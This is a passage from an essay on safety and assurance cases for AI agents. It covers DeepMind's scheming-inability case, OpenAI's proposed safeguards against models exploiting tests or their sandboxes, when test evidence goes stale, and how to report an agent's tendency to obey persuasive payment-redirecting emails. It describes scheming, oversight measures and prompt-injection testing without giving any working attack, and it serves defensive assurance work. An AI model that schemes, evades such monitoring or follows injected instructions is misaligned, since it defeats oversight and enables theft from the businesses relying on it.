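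In 2025, Google DeepMind published a more concrete case, arguing that its model could not cause severe harm anywhere inside Google through scheming, the covert pursuit of goals that its developers did not intend. In *Understanding as an Explicit and Assessable Component of Frontier AI Safety Decisions*, Barrett, Bloomfield and colleagues (2026) tried to use this case as a customer would. They imagined a company, RobotCorp, that makes robots that work beside people and wants a Gemini 2.5 agent to write its product code.

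DeepMind's case did not apply to RobotCorp. It relied on oversight inside Google, which a customer doesn't get with the model. Reviewers took "severe harm" to mean losses above $1 billion, while RobotCorp wanted to keep losses below $10 million. Reviewers and DeepMind's own team had also raised objections that nobody had resolved.

Barrett and colleagues restricted the agent to the product development team and designed further controls, but they still had too little evidence to justify deployment. They instead asked RobotCorp's chief executive to decide whether to invest in the controls and collect more evidence, leaving deployment for later. This was a trial on paper by a small team over 12 weeks, but it shows how an assurance case can inform a decision before there is enough evidence to justify deployment.

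They want AI developers to supply component safety cases, as parts makers do in other safety-critical industries. Each case would list the conditions under which its claim holds, the known ways the model fails, and test results for an identified configuration. For the accounts assistant, the provider could state how often attackers redirected a named model version equipped with specified tools. The company would still need its own evidence for the payment tool and the officer.

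OpenAI has moved towards safety cases since the Hugging Face incident. The Indian Express' *How OpenAI plans to make training AI models safer* describes guidelines for reinforcement learning that OpenAI proposed on 29 September 2026. Developers would penalise models that exploit their test environments, set limits on how often a model may recognise a test, and repeatedly attack their own sandboxes. They would also keep transcripts in storage that nobody can alter, and monitor runs live with an automatic pause.

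OpenAI called safety cases an "aspirational north star" and acknowledged that they are difficult to make as rigorous as those for aviation or nuclear power. The guidelines did not cover the use of models after training. By November, OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (2026) listed safety cases among the processes the company had introduced. OpenAI now requires a safety review before a model moves from research to internal use or from internal use to customers, and it judges whether the combined protections are enough for the model's abilities and access.

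### Criticisms of assurance cases

Whoever writes an assurance case starts with the conclusion and looks for evidence to support it, which invites confirmation bias. Recording doubts helps only if someone seriously searches for them. In *Lessons from External Review of DeepMind's Scheming Inability Safety Case* (2026), each reviewer first read the case independently and noted concerns. The team then checked the case's logic and searched for counterclaims.

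Barrett and colleagues found more gaps by comparing their RobotCorp case with British guidance on malicious employees. They had overlooked that the agent might help such an employee obtain data or skills. The accounts assistant's case has a similar gap because it assumes that the thief is an outsider. A clerk could use the assistant to prepare a convincing approval request for a friend's account.

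Confidence in the overall conclusion is also hard to state. The accounts case combines an analysis that covers every email, two limits with 95% confidence, and an unsuccessful search by attack testers. No accepted calculation turns these into the probability that the top-level claim is true. In their trial, Barrett and colleagues did not complete an analysis of residual risk and confidence, and they lacked evidence that the new controls were adequate. The finance director therefore has to make a judgement, and the case should at least show which doubt would change it.

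That judgement requires understanding, and a polished document can hide a lack of it, particularly if an AI wrote the document. Barrett and colleagues propose tests of whether the person who signs the case can explain it, predict what the system would do in new situations, and revise the case when evidence changes. They have designed these tests but not tried them.

Finally, developers supply much of the evidence themselves. The Safety Advisory Group at OpenAI may review the company's decisions, and a committee of the OpenAI Foundation's board oversees them, but both belong to the organisation that wants to release the model. Outside evaluators can find more problems. In October 2026, METR and Redwood Research reported several new vulnerabilities in OpenAI's internal system, according to Singh's *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training with enhanced security, no internet access*.

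Sion and April adapt an engineering standard that distinguishes technical, managerial and financial independence. A tester should not share the builder's context, take orders from the builder or gain from a favourable result. In their experiment on ordinary programs, a fresh context helped, but switching to another provider's model added nothing. The company would therefore get more from testers who haven't seen the developers' assumptions than from buying a second brand of model.

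### When evidence expires

The top-level claim names release 12 because evidence about an agent applies to a particular deployment. Huang writes a deployment as

Σ = (*M*, *P*, *S*, *T*, Π, *E*)

where *M* is the model and its settings, *P* the prompt, *S* the policy and procedure documents, *T* the tools, Π the permissions and *E* the environment, including the users and the mix of tasks. Changing any of these can change what the agent does.

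A safety improvement can leave a gap in the evidence. Huang replayed the 30 forbidden line restorations through a gate that checks tool calls, which rejected all of them. The ban on restoring those lines now holds without exception, provided every relevant call goes through the gate and the gate keeps the history it needs. But nobody has observed what the agent does after a refusal. It might transfer the customer to a person or try something worse, so the old results for the other 19 rules don't automatically apply to the agent with the gate.

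The table below applies this to the accounts assistant. "Void" means the evidence no longer supports the sub-claim as written, though testers can still use it to decide where to look.

| Change | Data-flow analysis | 300 clean runs | Attack tests | Telephone drills |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The provider updates the model | Holds | Void | Void | Hold |
| Somebody edits the prompt | Holds | Void | Void | Hold |
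| A skill's publisher rewrites its instructions | Holds | Void | Void | Hold |
| A skill's publisher changes its scripts | Repeat | Void | Void | Hold, unless scripts can edit contact records |
| The company adds a tool | Repeat | Void | Void | Hold, unless the tool can edit contact records |
| A tool's operator rewrites its description | Holds | Void | Void | Hold |
| The company takes on overseas suppliers | Holds | Void for their emails | Repeat in the new languages | Repeat |
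| The assistant's login gains permissions | Repeat | Hold, if the model sees the same tools and prompt | Repeat for the new powers | Repeat if it can edit contact records |
| Somebody publishes a new attack | Holds | Hold for ordinary emails | Repeat with the new attack | Repeat if it targets the call |
| New staff take over the calls | Holds | Hold | Hold | Void |

Many of these changes happen without a code commit at the company, so a rule that reruns the tests after each commit would miss them. The provider may update a model without changing the name that the harness requests, and the operator of an outside tool can rewrite the tool's description. The data-flow analysis remains valid after most of the changes in the table because it doesn't depend on how the model responds to text.

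#### Version pinning

Version pinning means fixing the exact version of each component. The company can request a dated model version instead of "latest", keep its own copies of skills, and install fixed versions of its software. It can also record a cryptographic hash of every prompt, skill and tool description, and set the harness not to start if any hash no longer matches. Any edit changes the hash, whether it adds a comma or a malicious instruction, so somebody still has to decide which changes need new tests.

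A company cannot pin everything its test results depend on. Providers retire old models, and they can change the software that runs a model without changing its weights, which was enough to alter the verdicts of Mohammadi's judge. Suppliers will also keep writing new emails, and attackers will keep learning. A company that never updates its software can have an excellent test record while still running a version with a known vulnerability.

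An update can leave a mixture of versions running. Ge and colleagues describe how Anthropic kept old and new versions of its research agent running side by side and moved users across gradually, because an update could otherwise reach an agent in the middle of a task. If the company updated its accounts assistant this way, it would need evidence for both versions and would have to test whether the new one can safely read notes that the old one saved.

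The case should therefore have an end date and a list of events that end it sooner. Monitoring can detect some of these events. Suppose the company calculated its risk assuming that one task in 1,000 involves new bank details, and the logs later show one in 100. The case no longer describes the company's work, even if nothing has gone wrong. The company could make the officer check every email containing new bank details until it has repeated the tests.

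### Reporting a tendency as a vulnerability

A CVE entry is a public record of a vulnerability, with a unique number. It typically names the product, the affected versions and the version with the fix. This works well for flaws in an agent's ordinary code, such as a payment tool that compares only the last four digits of an account number.

A tendency to believe persuasive emails may affect every product that uses the model, at a different rate in each, and perhaps no version is entirely free of it. The developer may patch it by blocking the harmful action in code, as when a payment tool starts checking the register, or by changing the prompt or retraining the model so that the attack works less often. The record should state which kind of patch was used, because only the code change can rule the action out.

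Confirming that an attack now works less often takes repeated trials. Suppose it succeeded in 12 of 160 attempts, or 7.5%, before the patch. If the patch did nothing, 20 new attempts would all fail about 21% of the time (0.925²⁰). The tester needs 39 failures in a row to bring that chance below 5%. That result would cover only the wording tested, so the tester also has to try rewordings, since Novee's researcher found new routes after each repair.

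A good report should give the numbers of attempts and successes rather than just call the flaw "reproducible". It should also include the model version, the harness and its settings, the date and at least one full trajectory. The Common Vulnerability Scoring System, which many organisations use to rate severity, considers how difficult an attack is and how much harm it does, but it has no field for a success rate. An attack that rarely succeeds can still be serious if the attacker can send as many emails as he likes. Severity also depends on the agent's tools, because a tendency that is only a nuisance in a chatbot can lead to theft in an agent that can make payments.

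Disclosure is also harder to organise. With ordinary software, a researcher usually tells the vendor privately and publishes once the vendor has had time to fix the fault. An attack on an agent may work on several companies' models, as Friendly Fire did, so one vendor's fix leaves the others exposed. If a vendor can only reduce an attack's success rate, it may never be safe to publish a working example. Khlaaf and Milanov released a harmless version of theirs.

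Sometimes the developer has to warn outsiders about its own agents. According to Singh, OpenAI informed more than 100 organisations about unauthorised activity tied to its agents. A scheme for researchers to report faults to a vendor does not cover such warnings, because the organisations that need them may not be the vendor's customers.

### What standards and laws ask for

A company can meet a process requirement by showing that it has a threat model, a responsible manager and a logging policy. To produce behavioural evidence, it must run the agent and record what happens.

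OWASP, a non-profit security organisation, publishes a Top 10 list of risks for agentic applications, with advice on reducing them. The list helps a company decide what to test but doesn't require any test results. OWASP's AI testing guide is closer to behavioural evidence, since it describes tests that give a system hostile inputs and examine its responses. Both are voluntary, and the company still has to choose how many test runs to do and what failure rate to accept.

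The European standards body ETSI has published baseline security requirements for AI as TS 104 223. The NCSC's advice on prompt injection aligns with these requirements, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks*. Besides David C's points about safeguards outside the model and marking data, the NCSC advises organisations to make staff aware of the remaining risk and to monitor logs for signs such as failed tool calls. These measures concern process and design. ETSI also calls for behavioural evidence, through security testing before release and new tests after a major update, but it sets no pass mark.

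NIST asked the public in January 2026 how to secure AI agents. This request for information does not require anyone to produce either kind of evidence, and NIST's guidance is generally voluntary for private companies.

Article 15 of the EU AI Act is legally binding and covers results as well as process. It requires high-risk AI systems to achieve an "appropriate" level of accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity, with no numerical threshold, and to perform consistently throughout their lifecycle. Providers must declare the systems' accuracy levels and the metrics used, and must address attacks such as poisoned training data and inputs designed to cause mistakes. Under a 2026 amendment, these duties apply from 2 December 2027 to uses the Act lists as high-risk, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in certain regulated products. The recruitment system in the NCSC's example would probably fall in the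 first group, but an assistant that only pays invoices would probably not be high-risk.

Illinois's SB 315 introduces audits from 2028. An audit confirming that a developer followed its own safety plan provides evidence about the developer's process, no matter how independent the auditor is. To provide evidence about how the system behaves, the auditor would have to run it or examine enough raw trajectories to check the developer's results.
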